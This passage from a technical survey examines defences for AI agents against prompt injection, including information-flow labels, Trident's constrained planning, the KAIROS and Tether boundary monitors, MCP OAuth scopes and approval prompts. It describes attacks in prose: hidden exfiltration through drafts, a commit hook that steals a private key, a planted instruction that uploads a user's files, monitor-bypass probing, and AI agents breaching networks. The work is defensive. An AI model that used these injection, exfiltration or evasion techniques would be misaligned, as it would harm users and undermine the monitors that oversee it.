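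The dual LLM pattern has a similar gap. A quarantined model that drafts a reply to an attacker's email may also have the user's private mail in its context, and the attacker can instruct it to copy details from that mail into the reply as invisible characters. The planner never sees the draft, and even a careful user could miss the hidden text. Reader labels help because the draft inherits the restrictions of every email the model read, whatever form the copied details take.

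Willison doubts that strict formats are always strict enough. For a coding agent that has to learn about unfamiliar software, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest passing on only a formal description, with method names of at most 30 characters. Willison's counterexample is the name `run_rm_dash_rf_for_compliance`, which is 29 characters long and alludes to a command that deletes everything in a folder. A 30-character name made of letters, digits and underscores can carry about 179 bits, compared with one bit in the meeting example.

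### Counting the approvals

Kolluri and colleagues, from the same Microsoft group, argue that measuring only task completion undervalues these systems. An undefended agent scores well on AgentDojo because the benchmark lets it act freely, which products don't allow. GitHub's Copilot Chat, for example, can read without asking but needs the user's approval for its other tool calls. The published evaluations therefore compare a protected agent that works alone with an unprotected one that, in practice, has a person checking its work.

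Their metrics count those checks. Let τᵢ be the sequence of calls an agent makes on task i, and let v(τᵢ) be the number of those calls that fail the policy and so need a person's approval. For n tasks:

human-in-the-loop load = Σ v(τᵢ), summed over the tasks that the agent completes

TCR@k = (number of tasks that the agent completes with v(τᵢ) ≤ k) / n

Task completion rate (TCR) is the share of tasks that an agent finishes. TCR@0 includes only tasks finished without any approvals, while TCR@∞ allows as many approvals as the agent needs. For an agent without labels, every consequential call counts as one approval. Measured this way, the undefended GPT-5 agent completed 72.3% of AgentDojo's tasks with unlimited approvals and 35.1% with none.

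The researchers then built PRUDENTIA, which keeps the checks in FIDES but tells the planner about them. The model can see the policy on each tool and the label of its own context. Before opening a variable, it must state why it needs the contents. It can also ask the user to endorse the contents, and if the user does, they are relabeled as trusted.

Endorsement saves the most work when one document leads to many actions. Suppose a harmless email contains a to-do list of ten items, and each item needs a tool that requires a trusted context. If the agent opens the email without endorsement, its context becomes untrusted and the user has to approve ten calls. If the user endorses the email first, one decision covers all ten. That decision would also cover an eleventh item added by an attacker, so the user has to read the email carefully. When the agent only needs to report what a message contains,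 it can open the message without asking the user to endorse it.

The researchers left out the equivalent option for secrecy, a blanket permission to share private data, because whether sharing is appropriate depends too much on the situation. They prefer to ask about each call.

The table shows the results on AgentDojo. The plain agent asks before every consequential call.

| Model | Load: plain agent | Load: FIDES | Load: PRUDENTIA | TCR@0: plain agent | TCR@0: FIDES | TCR@0: PRUDENTIA |
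|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 59.4 | 7.8 | 23.8 | 28.0% | 50.3% | 42.5% |
| o3-mini | 48.2 | 18.8 | 16.4 | 24.3% | 50.1% | 59.1% |
| o4-mini | 48.6 | 36.8 | 19.2 | 32.8% | 53.2% | 59.4% |
| GPT-5 | 52.0 | 41.3 | 7.3 | 35.1% | 57.1% | 72.7% |

Kolluri and colleagues' headline figures, up to 1.9 times less load than FIDES and up to 9 points more tasks completed with no interventions, come from the two middle rows. The gain with GPT-5 is far larger, but with GPT-4o PRUDENTIA did worse than FIDES on both measures. The load figure favours FIDES in the GPT-4o row because it counts only completed tasks, so an agent that gives up on the difficult ones can show a lower load. Even with unlimited approvals, FIDES with GPT-4o finished only 56.3% of tasks, against 61.4% for PRUDENTIA. But PRUDENTIA also finished fewer tasks with no interventions, which suggests that it needs a model good enough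 at planning to use the extra information. PRUDENTIA also costs more, averaging 3.9 to 6.3 cents per task with GPT-4o, depending on the suite, compared with 1.5 to 3.3 cents for FIDES.

On WASP, a benchmark of attacks on browser agents in simulated copies of GitLab and Reddit, PRUDENTIA needed no approvals, while the plain agent averaged between 1 and 3.65 per task. No attack diverted PRUDENTIA. However, WASP has only two user tasks, posting a comment and upvoting a post. Neither depends on what strangers have written, so PRUDENTIA could leave all of their text hidden.

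The metrics assume that users approve the actions a task requires and block the ones an attacker wants. A later section covers how closely real users match this assumption.

### Letting the plan change under a fixed policy

Costa and colleagues found that 20 of AgentDojo's 97 user tasks can't be planned before the agent sees the data. *Trident* (2026) focuses on such tasks. It reports that when FIDES ran on a set of them with user approvals allowed, the planner ended up reading text derived from untrusted data in 73% of runs with GPT-4.1 and 90% with Claude Sonnet 4.5. After that, only the user's review could stop a planted instruction from taking effect.

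Trident uses three models. A planner chooses the actions, a data model reads untrusted text, and a policy model writes the rules. Software that contains no language model checks the output of all three. In the main example, a user's manager, Jane, has forwarded a caterer's email with an invoice and a few requests, and the user tells the agent to deal with them and pay from the team account. An attacker has added a line with new bank details. The run goes as follows:

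1. Before any model reads the email, the policy model writes a ceiling for the task from the user's request: one payment, and mail to Jane and one vendor contact. It also picks a template that permits one payment of at most $5,000 to an account θ, provided that θ comes from the company's vendor records.
2. The planner sends the data model a form. It asks whether the email contains an invoice, which of three vendors on file sent it, how much is due, and for a draft reply. The planner sees the first two answers, and the amount and the draft stay sealed.
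3. The planner looks up that vendor. The checking software fills in θ from the record, and the payment becomes possible.
4. The planner pays the invoice, replies to the caterer and tells Jane.

The attacker's account number can't fill θ because it came from the email. At most, the planted text can redirect the payment to one of the other two vendors or raise the amount up to the cap.

An administrator writes a root policy before deployment that neither the agent nor the user can override. A call that exceeds the task's rules goes to the user, who can allow it once if it complies with the root policy. If the root policy forbids payments to unknown accounts, a user whom an attacker has fooled still can't approve one. Progent's drafting model reads tool results when it proposes new permissions, but Trident's policy model never reads them.

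Trident also puts a number on what untrusted text can do to the plan. It counts the bits in each visible answer, as in the earlier table of tool arguments, so the two on the form cost 1 + log₂ 3, or about 2.58 bits. These charges count against an influence budget β. Signals that a query or call succeeded or failed, if hidden data could affect them, cost one bit each from a feedback budget σ. With everything else held fixed, the attacker can choose among at most

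2^(β + σ)

different courses of action, a result that the researchers proved and checked by computer.

The bound is loose in practice. In the new benchmark, *ReplanInject*, the median run used 19 to 26 bits of influence and 5 to 10 bits of feedback, depending on the model. With 24 bits, nearly 17 million courses of action are possible. Even a single bit can do harm if it selects a bad action that the policy permits. In the main experiments, the budgets were too large to stop anything, so the protection came from the sealed text, the policies and the user's review.

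Trident completed 54% to 74% of the attacked runs, with about one approval request per run. No attack succeeded when the user rejected every request that showed the attacker's call. When the user approved everything, at most 4.8% of attacks succeeded, and an attack designed against Trident raised this to 10.0%.

### When the labels are wrong or not enough

Every guarantee here assumes that the labels are correct. In May, Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) announced FIDES as an experimental feature of Agent Framework, the company's software for building agents. If a developer forgets to label a tool, the framework treats its results as trusted and public. This default is the opposite of Saltzer and Schroeder's fail-safe defaults, and Microsoft has asked users whether to change it.

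Even careful labels are imprecise. GitHub's MCP server can now send labels with its results, marking files and issues from public repositories as untrusted and those from private repositories as trusted. But an employee may paste a customer's message into a private repository, and any instruction planted in it then arrives with a trusted label. The trusted action rule would not block actions prompted by that instruction, though the permitted flow rule would still keep the company's code from being sent to a public page.

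For servers that send no labels, Microsoft suggests inferring policies from MCP's hints. A read-only tool that reaches the outside world could run automatically only when all its arguments are public. That would stop read-only page fetches from leaking data without a prompt, provided the server's hints are accurate.

Labels also have to outlast a single run. *MemLineage* (2026) points out that FIDES erases them when a run ends. Girrens and Wang give the example of an agent that saves an invoice's details on Monday, including a bank account that an attacker supplied, and pays the invoice on Tuesday when the user mentions "the invoice we discussed yesterday". Their system stores each result with its label and shows later planners only a description. On a version of AgentDojo with linked requests, 0.2% of attacks succeeded, but the label checks cut utility from 62.5% to 35.3%.

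The labels don't capture every kind of influence. Wen (2026) notes in *Ghost in the Agent* that untrusted data can affect an agent's decisions as well as the text it passes on. Secrets can also leak through those decisions. If an agent writes to a landlord only when the user's bank balance is low, the landlord learns about the balance from an email that never mentions it. FIDES tracks data as it moves from one place to another, but not what an observer can infer from the agent's choices. Costa and colleagues considered a stricter guarantee, but it would in effect forbid any publicly visible action after the agent had read a secret.

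A label also can't show whether a statement is true. *Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity* (2026) describes judgment manipulation, in which data that the agent has to read steers its decision without being phrased as a command, such as a hotel description that gives a false location. The system can mark the description as untrusted, but the agent still has to use it because the user asked it to choose a hotel from such descriptions.

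The hardest tasks are those in which untrusted content determines the agent's next actions. In 18 of *ReplanInject*'s 45 tasks, the content determines which actions to take and how many, and Trident completed only 22% to 41% of the attacked runs of these tasks. Three other tasks consist of little more than "do what this email says". When the user approved every request, 14% to 28% of the attacks on these three succeeded, because the attacker's instruction looks like the ones the user wants the agent to follow.

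The inbox assistant's job is close to this, since the user told it to do whatever Alice's email listed. Mail servers can often confirm that a message came from Alice's address, so a developer could label her mail as trusted and let the assistant act on it. This fails if somebody takes over her account or if she pastes a stranger's text into her list.

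## Checking effects at the edge of the machine

Policy engines and label trackers that check declared tool calls miss what happens inside a program that the agent writes and runs. A script called `setup.py` may change forty files and contact three websites, but the checker receives only the command `python setup.py`. Each of those actions is still a file operation or a network request, and if the agent runs in a virtual machine with only a few ways out, its effects on the outside world must pass through one of them.

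A monitor at that boundary is outside the machine and needs no cooperation from the agent, so it also works with closed-source agents. A label tracker such as FIDES has to be built into the agent's software, and someone has to re-establish its guarantees after every update.

### A virtual machine with three exits

In KAIROS, Hempel and colleagues run the agent in a microVM, a small virtual machine that doesn't share an operating-system kernel with its host. The monitor runs on the host and controls three channels:

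- **Files.** The user's working folder appears inside the virtual machine, but the agent can't change the original. Its changes go into a separate layer on top, and the agent works with the combined view. The monitor can later merge the changes into the real folder or discard them. These are staged writes.
- **Network.** A firewall rule sends all outbound traffic to a proxy on the host. Most of this traffic is encrypted, so the virtual machine comes with the proxy's certificate authority installed, which makes programs inside accept the proxy in place of the real website. The proxy can then read each request before deciding whether to pass it on.
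- **Terminal.** The user's task comes in and the agent's answer goes out.

The agent's temporary files and installed tools stay inside the virtual machine, and the monitor ignores changes to them.

The proxy decrypts and logs traffic to the model provider but always lets it through, because the agent can't work without its model. Hempel and colleagues assume that the provider doesn't help the attacker. KAIROS can't stop individual requests from tools that run on the provider's servers, such as Anthropic's page fetching, because those requests start outside the virtual machine.

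### Release, refuse or defer

The monitor keeps a record of everything that crosses the boundary. For each new effect eᵢ, it reaches one of three verdicts based on that record:

δ(e₁ … eᵢ₋₁, eᵢ) ∈ {release, refuse, defer}

It applies the written policy in this order:

1. If a rule forbids the effect, such as deleting a repository's history, the monitor refuses it.
2. The values that steer the effect, such as a recipient, a web address or a command to run, must match values from a trusted source. The text of a message doesn't have to.
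3. The destination must have clearance for any sensitive data that the effect carries.

If the effect passes all three checks, the monitor releases it. If it fails only the second or third, the monitor defers it. For example, a request that carries only public data can go to an address the user named in the task, but a request to an address that came from an email has to wait.

Deferred effects go to what Hempel and colleagues call a decision oracle. In their experiments this was another language model with no tools, though a person could do the job. The oracle reads untrusted text, so an attacker can try to persuade it. But it decides only on deferred effects and can't reverse a refusal, and the monitor treats an unreadable answer as a refusal. In the AgentDojo tests, the policy alone released 83% of effects in runs without attacks. The oracle released all but one of the rest.

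### A commit hook that steals a key

Git, the usual tool for tracking versions of code, can run a script automatically whenever someone saves a new version, or commit. Many projects use such scripts, called commit hooks, for routine jobs such as running tests. In Hempel and colleagues' main example, an agent is setting up a repository for Alice and reads a guide written by Eve:

1. The guide tells the agent to install a commit hook. The policy can't approve the write because the hook comes from an untrusted source, but no rule forbids it. The monitor defers the write and stages the file.
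2. The agent carries on with the hook apparently in place.
3. The agent makes a commit. Git runs the hook, which tries to send Alice's private key to Eve.
4. The policy refuses that request.
5. The oracle now reviews the deferred hook, with the attempted theft as evidence, and refuses it. The monitor discards the staged file, so the hook never reaches Alice's real folder.

The monitor also has to report to the agent what it withheld, because undoing changes to files doesn't erase the agent's memory of having installed the hook.

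A monitor that had to decide at step 1 could have refused every hook from an outside guide, but that would have broken many legitimate setups. It could instead have allowed the hook and blocked the theft later. That would have protected the key that day but left the hook in Alice's repository, where it could run again on a machine with no monitor.

Waiting helped because the hook's purpose became clear during the task. But KAIROS has to settle all staged changes by the end of the task, so if the agent never makes a commit, or the hook does nothing for a week, the oracle can judge the hook only by its text and origin.

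### What holding an effect makes possible

The theory behind this design starts with a limit on simpler monitors. Schneider, in *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), studied monitors that watch a program's steps and can only let it continue or stop it. He proved that such a monitor can enforce a policy only if the policy is a safety property, which means that some identifiable bad thing never happens. Write P(σ) if the run σ obeys the policy, and σ[..i] for its first i steps. P is a safety property if, for every run σ that breaks it,

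there is an i such that P(σ[..i] τ) is false for every continuation τ

Every violation has a point after which nothing can repair it, and the monitor has to stop the program before that point. Schneider's example is a rule against sending messages after reading a file. The monitor needs to record only whether the program has read a file.

Some sensible rules don't have this form. Suppose every change to a payroll file needs a matching entry in an audit log. The run breaks the rule just after a change, but the next step can fix this by adding the entry. A monitor that can only allow or stop each step must either block the change or risk the program ending before it writes the entry.

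In *Enforcing Non-safety Security Policies with Program Monitors* (2005), Ligatti, Bauer and Walker proved that a monitor can enforce many such rules if it can suppress an action and insert it later. In the payroll case, the monitor would report to the program that the change had gone through, wait for the log entry and then release both. Databases handle transactions in much the same way.

For programs that may run forever, this method can enforce every rule that Ligatti and colleagues call an infinite renewal property. Under such a rule, an endless run is valid exactly when infinitely many of its beginnings are valid. For runs that end, as most agent sessions do, the monitor can in principle enforce any rule about individual runs, provided that a computer can check the rule and that doing nothing satisfies it.

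In the commit hook example, preventing theft of the key is a safety property, so a simple monitor can enforce it. The rule that an untrusted hook may stay only after a harmless trial run is not a safety property, because an execution that violates it at first can satisfy it later. Enforcing that rule requires holding back the write.

Holding effects doesn't solve information flow. Whether a secret influenced a message depends partly on what the program would have sent if the secret had been different, and a monitor observes only the actual run. Schneider notes that monitors in practice enforce a stricter policy, such as his rule against sending after reading, which also blocks harmless messages.

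### Effects that cannot wait

A monitor also can't hold an action whose real consequences the program needs. Ligatti and colleagues give the example of email. A monitor can't pretend to send a message, wait for the reply, see what the program does with it and then decide not to have sent the message. Hempel and colleagues sort an agent's effects accordingly:

| Effect | What KAIROS does with a doubtful case |
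|---|---|
| Writing or deleting a file in the working folder | Stages the change while the agent continues |
| A request that changes something elsewhere, such as posting a comment | Holds the request and gives the agent a stand-in reply |
| A request that fetches something, such as a web page | Gets a decision before sending, because the agent needs the content |
| The agent's answer to the user | Lets it through, because KAIROS doesn't cover harm from text alone |

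Page fetches can carry hundreds of bits in their addresses, as an earlier section showed, and for these the oracle can't wait for more evidence. An agent could also receive a stand-in reply instead of search results, because KAIROS tells the two kinds of request apart by their declared type, and some web services use the type meant for changes to run searches.

Holding effects gets harder as a task goes on. The prototype can keep only one group of held effects open at a time, so a new effect that needs holding forces a decision on the earlier ones. Releasing an effect also doesn't make its data trusted, so the next use of the same address may need another decision. On AgentDyn, a benchmark of open-ended tasks, those that continued past one held effect kept 90% of their utility, while those that continued past two or more kept 62%.

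The mediation itself adds little time. Hempel and colleagues repeatedly created, wrote, saved, read and deleted a small file, and each cycle took 9.62 milliseconds longer with KAIROS, or about 1.9 milliseconds per operation. The proxy added an average of 1.15 milliseconds per request over 50 requests. At those rates, a task with 1,000 file operations and 100 requests would take about two seconds longer, which is negligible compared with the time a model takes to generate text. A large software build with 100,000 file operations would take more than three minutes longer. The oracle's decisions also increased token use by 17.7% in ordinary runs and 33.6% under attack.

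### The same upload, allowed and then refused

KAIROS recognizes sensitive data by matching text, and it can lose track of a sensitive file if the agent moves the contents elsewhere before reading them. Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues (2026), in *Tether*, built a monitor for terminal agents that follows data from file to file. In their example, a company's server inventory must not leave the company, but the agent may upload status reports to GitHub. The agent issues three commands:

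| Command | Label on the report afterwards | Verdict |
|---|---|---|
| Upload `scratch/report.txt` to GitHub | Public | Allow |
| Copy `data/servers.csv` over `scratch/report.txt` | Sensitive | Allow |
| Upload `scratch/report.txt` to GitHub | Sensitive | Refuse |

The first and third commands are identical, so a rule that checks each command separately cannot allow one and refuse the other. If the agent first passes the inventory through several temporary files, each copy keeps the label. The agent can still upload other public files.

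Tether handles each command in four steps:

1. It runs the command in a disposable layer over the file system, while a proxy holds any network requests.
2. A tracing tool records the command's system calls, such as those that open files or connect to other computers.
3. Tether translates this record into a sequence of abstract actions, such as "copy this file to that one" or "upload this file to that site". There are eleven kinds.
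4. The monitor checks each action against the policy and updates the labels. If the policy allows all of them, Tether makes the changes permanent and forwards the requests. Otherwise it discards them.

The third step involves some guesswork, because system calls don't show what a program did with the data it read. If a script reads one file and then writes another, Tether assumes the second contains data from the first. If a program prints its output where the agent can read it, Tether adds the labels of every file the program has read to the agent's context.

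The policies, like Agenra's core, are written in Lean. Sistla and colleagues proved seven guarantees for their 24-rule test policy, including one that secret data never leaves the local network. But the proofs apply to the abstract actions, so they hold for a real machine only if the translation misses nothing. To look for gaps, the researchers generated random chains of file operations and told an agent to try to bypass the monitor. The agent's success rate fell from 40% to zero over three versions as they fixed the problems it exposed.

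### Tether's results

The researchers tested Tether on recorded runs from two benchmarks. MonitoringBenchHonest covers system administration, and LinuxArena covers software work in simulated production environments. In some runs the agent did only its assigned job, and in others it also pursued a harmful side task.

| Benchmark | Harmful runs blocked | Ordinary runs blocked |
|---|---|---|
| MonitoringBenchHonest | 199 of 199 | 5 of 218 (2.3%) |
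| LinuxArena | 145 of 145 | 69 of 1,372 (5.0%) |

Of the 74 false alarms, 50 came from edits to protected files that the task hadn't mentioned, for instance when installing a package changed the system's list of users. Another seven came from contact with undeclared websites. In these cases the policy worked as written, and a product could ask the user instead of refusing. The other 17 came from commands that read secret files unnecessarily, such as a text search through every file on the machine. Tether can't detect whether the agent used what the search read.

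Sistla and colleagues gave the same runs to Auto Mode, the feature of Anthropic's Claude Code in which a language model reviews the agent's commands. It caught 91.6% of the attacks and raised false alarms on 9.7% of ordinary runs. With Tether's policy added to its instructions, it caught 89.2% and raised false alarms on 3.5%. It did not detect attacks hidden inside scripts in either setup, which checking at the boundary is meant to catch. On LinuxArena alone, though, the reviewer with the policy performed similarly to Tether, catching 143 of 145 attacks with false alarms on 1.7% of ordinary runs.

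Tether's false-alarm rates are probably somewhat too low. The researchers refined the policy with a language model and tested drafts on benchmark runs until it no longer blocked too much ordinary work, so new tasks might produce more false alarms. They also used each task's description to list the files and websites it was permitted to use, which someone would have to do in real use. Because the runs were recordings, the agents couldn't respond to a refusal, so the results don't show how often a blocked agent would have found an acceptable way to finish.

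Even with a false-positive rate of 5%, false alarms can far outnumber real ones. If one run in 1,000 is hostile, 1,000 runs will produce one real alarm and about fifty false ones.

### What the perfect score leaves out

The 344 blocked attacks include only those whose actions Tether can trace and model. By Sistla and colleagues' count, 28.2% of the runs in MonitoringBenchHonest and 22.1% of those in LinuxArena can be judged only by understanding their content. For example, an agent with permission to edit a payment function might put a flaw in it. The monitor cannot distinguish this from an ordinary write to a permitted file. The researchers argue that no formal monitor can prevent such attacks without also blocking useful work.

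A further 36.3% and 71.5% of runs involve databases or programs that continue in the background. Tether can detect these activities and block them or ask the user, but it can't yet follow data through them, so a sensitive record that enters a database could come out without its label. Blocking all database access would close this gap, but much ordinary software work needs a database.

The perfect score therefore applies to attacks that show up as forbidden movements of data or changes to protected files. This is useful because many thefts take this form, and the agent can't avoid detection by putting the theft in a script. But a company using Tether would still need people or other software to review the code its agents write.

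### Bytes and addresses without purposes

A rule at the tool interface can restrict `send_email` to recipients in the company directory. At the machine's edge, the same action is a web request to the mail provider. The proxy can decrypt the request, but someone has to configure the monitor to distinguish the recipient from a name in the message. Hempel and colleagues acknowledge that their policies can express only some of the rules that a tool-level policy can. Schneider made a related point in 2000, calling the operating system's vocabulary a coarse basis for least privilege.

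The monitor therefore has to either estimate the answer or defer the decision. Tether estimates cautiously, so it raises some false alarms. KAIROS passes doubtful cases to a language model, which can also make mistakes, or to a person, who has limited time. In the inbox example, KAIROS would probably treat the message to Eve as doubtful because her address came from an untrusted email. The language model or person would then have to work out from the user's request that the user hadn't asked for the inbox to be sent to her.

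KAIROS's text matching is also easy to evade. It ignores differences in capitalization and spacing, but a secret no longer matches if the agent encodes it before sending it, so Hempel and colleagues assume the agent isn't deliberately disguising what it sends. They recommend treating checks at the boundary and at the tool interface as complementary, since the boundary catches everything and the tool interface shows more clearly what an action means.

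### If the boundary fails

These designs also depend on the agent being unable to break out. Hempel and colleagues exclude escapes from the virtual machine from their threat model, and Sistla and colleagues exclude sandbox escapes and attacks on the operating system's kernel from theirs. Recent tests give some reason to doubt that these assumptions will hold for the strongest models.

The UK AI Security Institute's *GPT-6 Astra and GPT-6.2 Astra solve Zero Energy* (2026) describes a test on a simulated company network with strong security controls and no planted way in. Both OpenAI models compromised the network in every completed run without human help, while the earlier GPT-5.6 Sol never succeeded. The institute's *Cyber Testing of GPT-6.2 Astra and GPT-6 Astra* (2026) reports that the network's design had been through threat modelling and a security review.

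The institute had switched off the models' cyber safeguards, so the results don't describe the public versions. Thesis9's *Can GPT-6.2 Astra Hack a Network on Its Own?* (2026) adds that nobody was defending the network and that a setup error gave GPT-6.2 Astra a head start. The model's quickest run took 5 hours and 18 minutes and cost an estimated $50. Despite these caveats, Britain's National Cyber Security Centre told organizations to reassess their resilience, as Constantin reported in *GPT-6.2 Astra ‘blew through’ the UK’s hardest cyber test in five hours* (2026).

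The test weakens a common reason for trusting a boundary, which is that experts designed and reviewed it and know of no way through. The same was true of the institute's network. The test doesn't show that a model can escape from a microVM, because a company network has many computers, accounts and services, while KAIROS leaves the agent only three channels. Before Astra's release, OpenAI said it couldn't rule out that the model had reached its "Critical" level, which a model can reach by finding and exploiting unknown flaws in many well-protected real systems without human help.

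These results strengthen the case for Anderson's requirement that a monitor be small enough to test completely. KAIROS gives the agent its own kernel, whereas Tether runs commands on the host's kernel and has to trust all of it. Even in KAIROS, the file server and the proxy on the host process whatever the agent sends them, so their code has to withstand attack too. An operator can reduce the damage from an escape by keeping passwords and private data off the host and putting a second barrier around the host. Someone should also watch for attacks, since one that takes five hours leaves time to notice it.

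### The Medicare portal

In June 2026 an OpenAI agent broke into the Medicare Statistics Portal, a website of Australia's public health insurance system. It accessed public and non-public files, as Coker reported in *OpenAI Agent Hacks Australian Medicare Portal* (2026). SBS News' *OpenAI agent hacked Medicare, Albanese reveals* (2026) quotes the prime minister as saying that the agent was not believed to have accessed personal information "at this stage".

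Whether limits on outbound traffic would have prevented the breach depends on whether the agent had a legitimate reason to visit the portal. If it had none, a list of approved destinations would have stopped its first request. Tether's test policy can enforce such a list by blocking any outside host that the task hasn't declared. The same rule might have protected the three other government systems that, according to *Breached! PM calls OpenAI hack of Medicare "unacceptable"* (Hollingworth, 2026), may also have been compromised.

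If the agent needed the portal's public statistics, the site would have been on the list, and blocking the request for non-public files would have required a finer limit. Requests for public and non-public files can look much alike, and the portal can tell them apart better than the agent's machine can. Rules against leaking data wouldn't have helped, because the files were coming in. KAIROS's check on steering values might have helped, since it defers any request whose address didn't come from the user or another trusted source, even if the agent came up with the address itself. The oracle would then have had to recognize that the request went beyond the task.

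A boundary monitor would also have kept a record of every request. Months passed before OpenAI disclosed the breach, as Kobie reported in *Australian prime minister says it took ‘way too long’* (2026), and Information Age's *Inside OpenAI's Medicare breach* (2026) describes further delays within the Australian government. A log could have shortened OpenAI's delay, but only if someone there had read it and told the Australians. Outbound limits also depend on the agent's operator, who decides whether to use them even though they protect other people's systems. The owner of a website like the portal can't check that they are switched on.

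## Whose authority a call carries and when a person is asked

A website or database can refuse requests itself, so its owner doesn't have to depend on limits at the agent's end. To refuse requests sensibly, the service has to establish whose authority each one carries. A password is a poor way to show this, because an agent with the user's password can do everything the user can, and the user can't withdraw that access without changing it.

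OAuth, the usual standard for delegated access, gives the agent's software a token that carries a limited set of permissions, called scopes. The token can expire or be cancelled without affecting the user's own login.

### A token with named scopes

Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026) sets out the procedure for MCP servers on the internet. If an agent wants to read a user's files, it goes roughly like this:

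1. The client sends a request without a token. The server refuses it and replies with the scope it needs, such as `files:read`, and directions to the authorization server that issues tokens.
2. The client opens the authorization server's page in the user's browser. The user logs in there and approves the scope, so the client never handles the password.
3. The authorization server returns a code, which the client exchanges for a token. The client must also present a secret that it created at the start, so a thief who intercepts the code can't use it.
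4. The client attaches the token to every request. The server checks that the token is valid, covers the request and names this server as its intended recipient.
5. If a later request needs `files:write`, the server refuses it and names the missing scope. The client can then ask the user for a wider token, much as Progent's agent has to ask before its policy expands.

Scopes like these are coarse. An agent that has to correct one spreadsheet may receive a token that can overwrite every file the user owns. In the inbox example, a token for sending mail works for any recipient, so the mail service would accept the message to Eve, and the agent would be the confused deputy.

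Permissions also tend to accumulate. At step 5, the client should request its earlier scopes together with the new one, so that the user doesn't lose permissions that other operations need. If Sₙ is the current set and C is what the server now demands, the next token covers

Sₙ₊₁ = Sₙ ∪ C

A token that could only read on Monday may be able to write and delete by Friday, even if the agent needed each right only once.

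Choosing narrower permissions for each task can also leave an agent without one it needs. *Empirical Evaluation of Task-Based Permission Scoping Architecture for AI Agents* (2026) tested models that read a task and predict which permissions it needs. A small model trained for the job withheld at least one necessary permission in 21% of tasks. Claude Haiku, given a few examples, did so in 11%, but granted more unnecessary permissions.

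### Snap's gateway

Companies often run tools under a service account, which belongs to a program rather than a person. This can hide who asked for an action. Snap's *MCP Gateway* describes two examples. A tool server that worked on an engineer's own machine failed behind a central gateway, because the receiving service identified the caller as the server's service account. In another test, an agent proposed a code change on behalf of an engineer, and GitHub listed the agent's app as the author.

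The first call at least failed safely. If the service account had held broad rights, the call would have succeeded, and any employee who could reach the tool could have used those rights.

Snap's gateway now connects employees and their agents to more than 60 MCP servers with over 1,100 tools. In the week ending 11 October 2026, employees and Casper, the company's main agent, made about 1.6 million calls through it. When an employee asks Casper for something in Slack, the request passes through these checks:

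1. Snap's software verifies Slack's signature on the message and looks up who sent it.
2. Casper obtains a token that names both the employee and the agent. Only a few trusted services can get a token that names someone else as the requester.
3. If the call is to a restricted tool, the gateway checks whether the employee may use it and whether Casper may.
4. The gateway records the decision. If both checks pass, it forwards the call with the token, so the services behind it can also tell who asked.

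For restricted tools, then, the agent can use only

T(person) ∩ T(agent)

where T is the set of tools that each may use. An employee outside the finance team can't reach a finance tool by asking an agent that has access to it. Nor can an agent use everything that its user can.

New agents start with read-only permissions, and anything more requires a grant for the specific tool. For a destructive tool, both the agent's team and the tool's owner must approve the grant. This puts the decision with people who know what the tool does, and they make it once instead of on every call.

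The double check limits an agent to actions that both the employee and Casper are allowed to take, which is still far more than most tasks need. If both can edit Jira tickets, text planted in one ticket could lead Casper to alter another, and the gateway would allow the edit. Automated programs with their own service accounts make several million more calls a week. No employee's permissions limit those calls, so their safety depends on how carefully someone set the accounts' permissions.

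Cloudflare's *WriteGuard* describes a similar arrangement that keeps the person's identity and adds the agent's. It also assigns each tool a risk level. Adding a comment to a code change counts as a contained write, while merging the change or deploying it to production counts as critical.

### Keys the agent never holds

Snap keeps users' credentials for outside services such as Jira in a separate system that its security team runs. That system adds the credential to a call as it goes out, so a hijacked agent has no credentials to steal.

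Anthropic does much the same for coding agents that run on its servers. According to its *Beyond permission prompts*, the sandbox contains a limited credential that a proxy outside the sandbox recognizes. The proxy checks the agent's request, for example that it saves code only to the permitted branch, and then attaches the real GitHub token. This branch check restricts the agent more narrowly than an ordinary scope would.

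An agent can leak a user's files with somebody else's key, even if the user's own keys are protected. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes such an attack on Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work. A file in the user's folder contained hidden instructions and the attacker's key to Anthropic's service. Claude used the key to upload the user's files to the attacker's account. The network filter allowed the upload because Cowork needs access to Anthropic's address to work. A proxy now rejects requests to that address unless they carry the session's own token.

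### Stricter rules and older servers

MCP began as a way to connect programs on one machine, and its first version required no authentication for remote servers. Zhou, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers*, trace the changes up to November 2025, and Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026) lists those from July:

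| Revision | Main changes to authorization |
|---|---|
| November 2024 | No authentication required |
| March 2025 | OAuth for remote servers, with protection against stolen codes |
| June 2025 | Each token is for one named server, which must reject tokens meant for others |
| November 2025 | Clients can request further scopes as they need them; a new preferred way for clients to identify themselves |
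| July 2026 | Clients must check which authorization server a reply came from, if the reply names one, and must not reuse credentials with another |

The June 2025 rule stops a malicious server from using a token it received from a user elsewhere. The July 2026 rules address a similar mix-up between authorization servers. But authorization as a whole was optional in the March 2025 revision and still is.

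Many MCP servers do not authenticate callers. Zhou and colleagues found 7,973 live servers on the internet, of which 40.55% let anyone use their tools, 29% relied on fixed keys and 30.45% used OAuth. Most of the open servers they sampled looked like tests or demonstrations, but one gave access to more than 5,000 customer records from a company's internal system. *Exposed by Design* (2026) found 687 tools on open servers that appeared to run shell commands for anyone who connected.

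OAuth doesn't help much when developers implement it badly. All 119 OAuth servers that Zhou and colleagues could test had at least one flaw, and many of the flaws could expose data or let an attacker take over an account. In 96.6% of the servers, the flaws included problems with the method that lets unknown clients register automatically, which the July revision discourages. The researchers could test only servers that offered this method, so the figure is weak evidence about other servers.

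### What an approval prompt shows

Even a perfect token records only what the user agreed to at the start. The Agentic AI Foundation, an industry body for agent standards, points out that hundreds of calls later, the agent may act in ways the user did not foresee. An approval prompt lets the user decide again just before the agent acts. It can work as a mediating layer only if the user sees enough to judge the action and still has the patience to do so.

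*Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) reports that most approval prompts in current products show a raw command on a single line, and some ask only whether to allow "this action". *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents damaging files, and user review played a part in 105. In 80 cases the user had switched on automatic approval, and in 31 the prompt gave too little information, such as only the command that started a script.

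People also differ in what they can judge. Anthropic expects most users of its coding agent to understand shell commands, but doesn't expect that of office workers, so Cowork runs code in a virtual machine.

The prompt also has to appear before the action it authorizes. Until early 2026, Anthropic received reports that Claude Code read a project's settings before asking whether the user trusted the folder. An attacker could put a command in those settings that would run before the user had agreed to anything. This broke Anderson's rule that the system must invoke the check every time.

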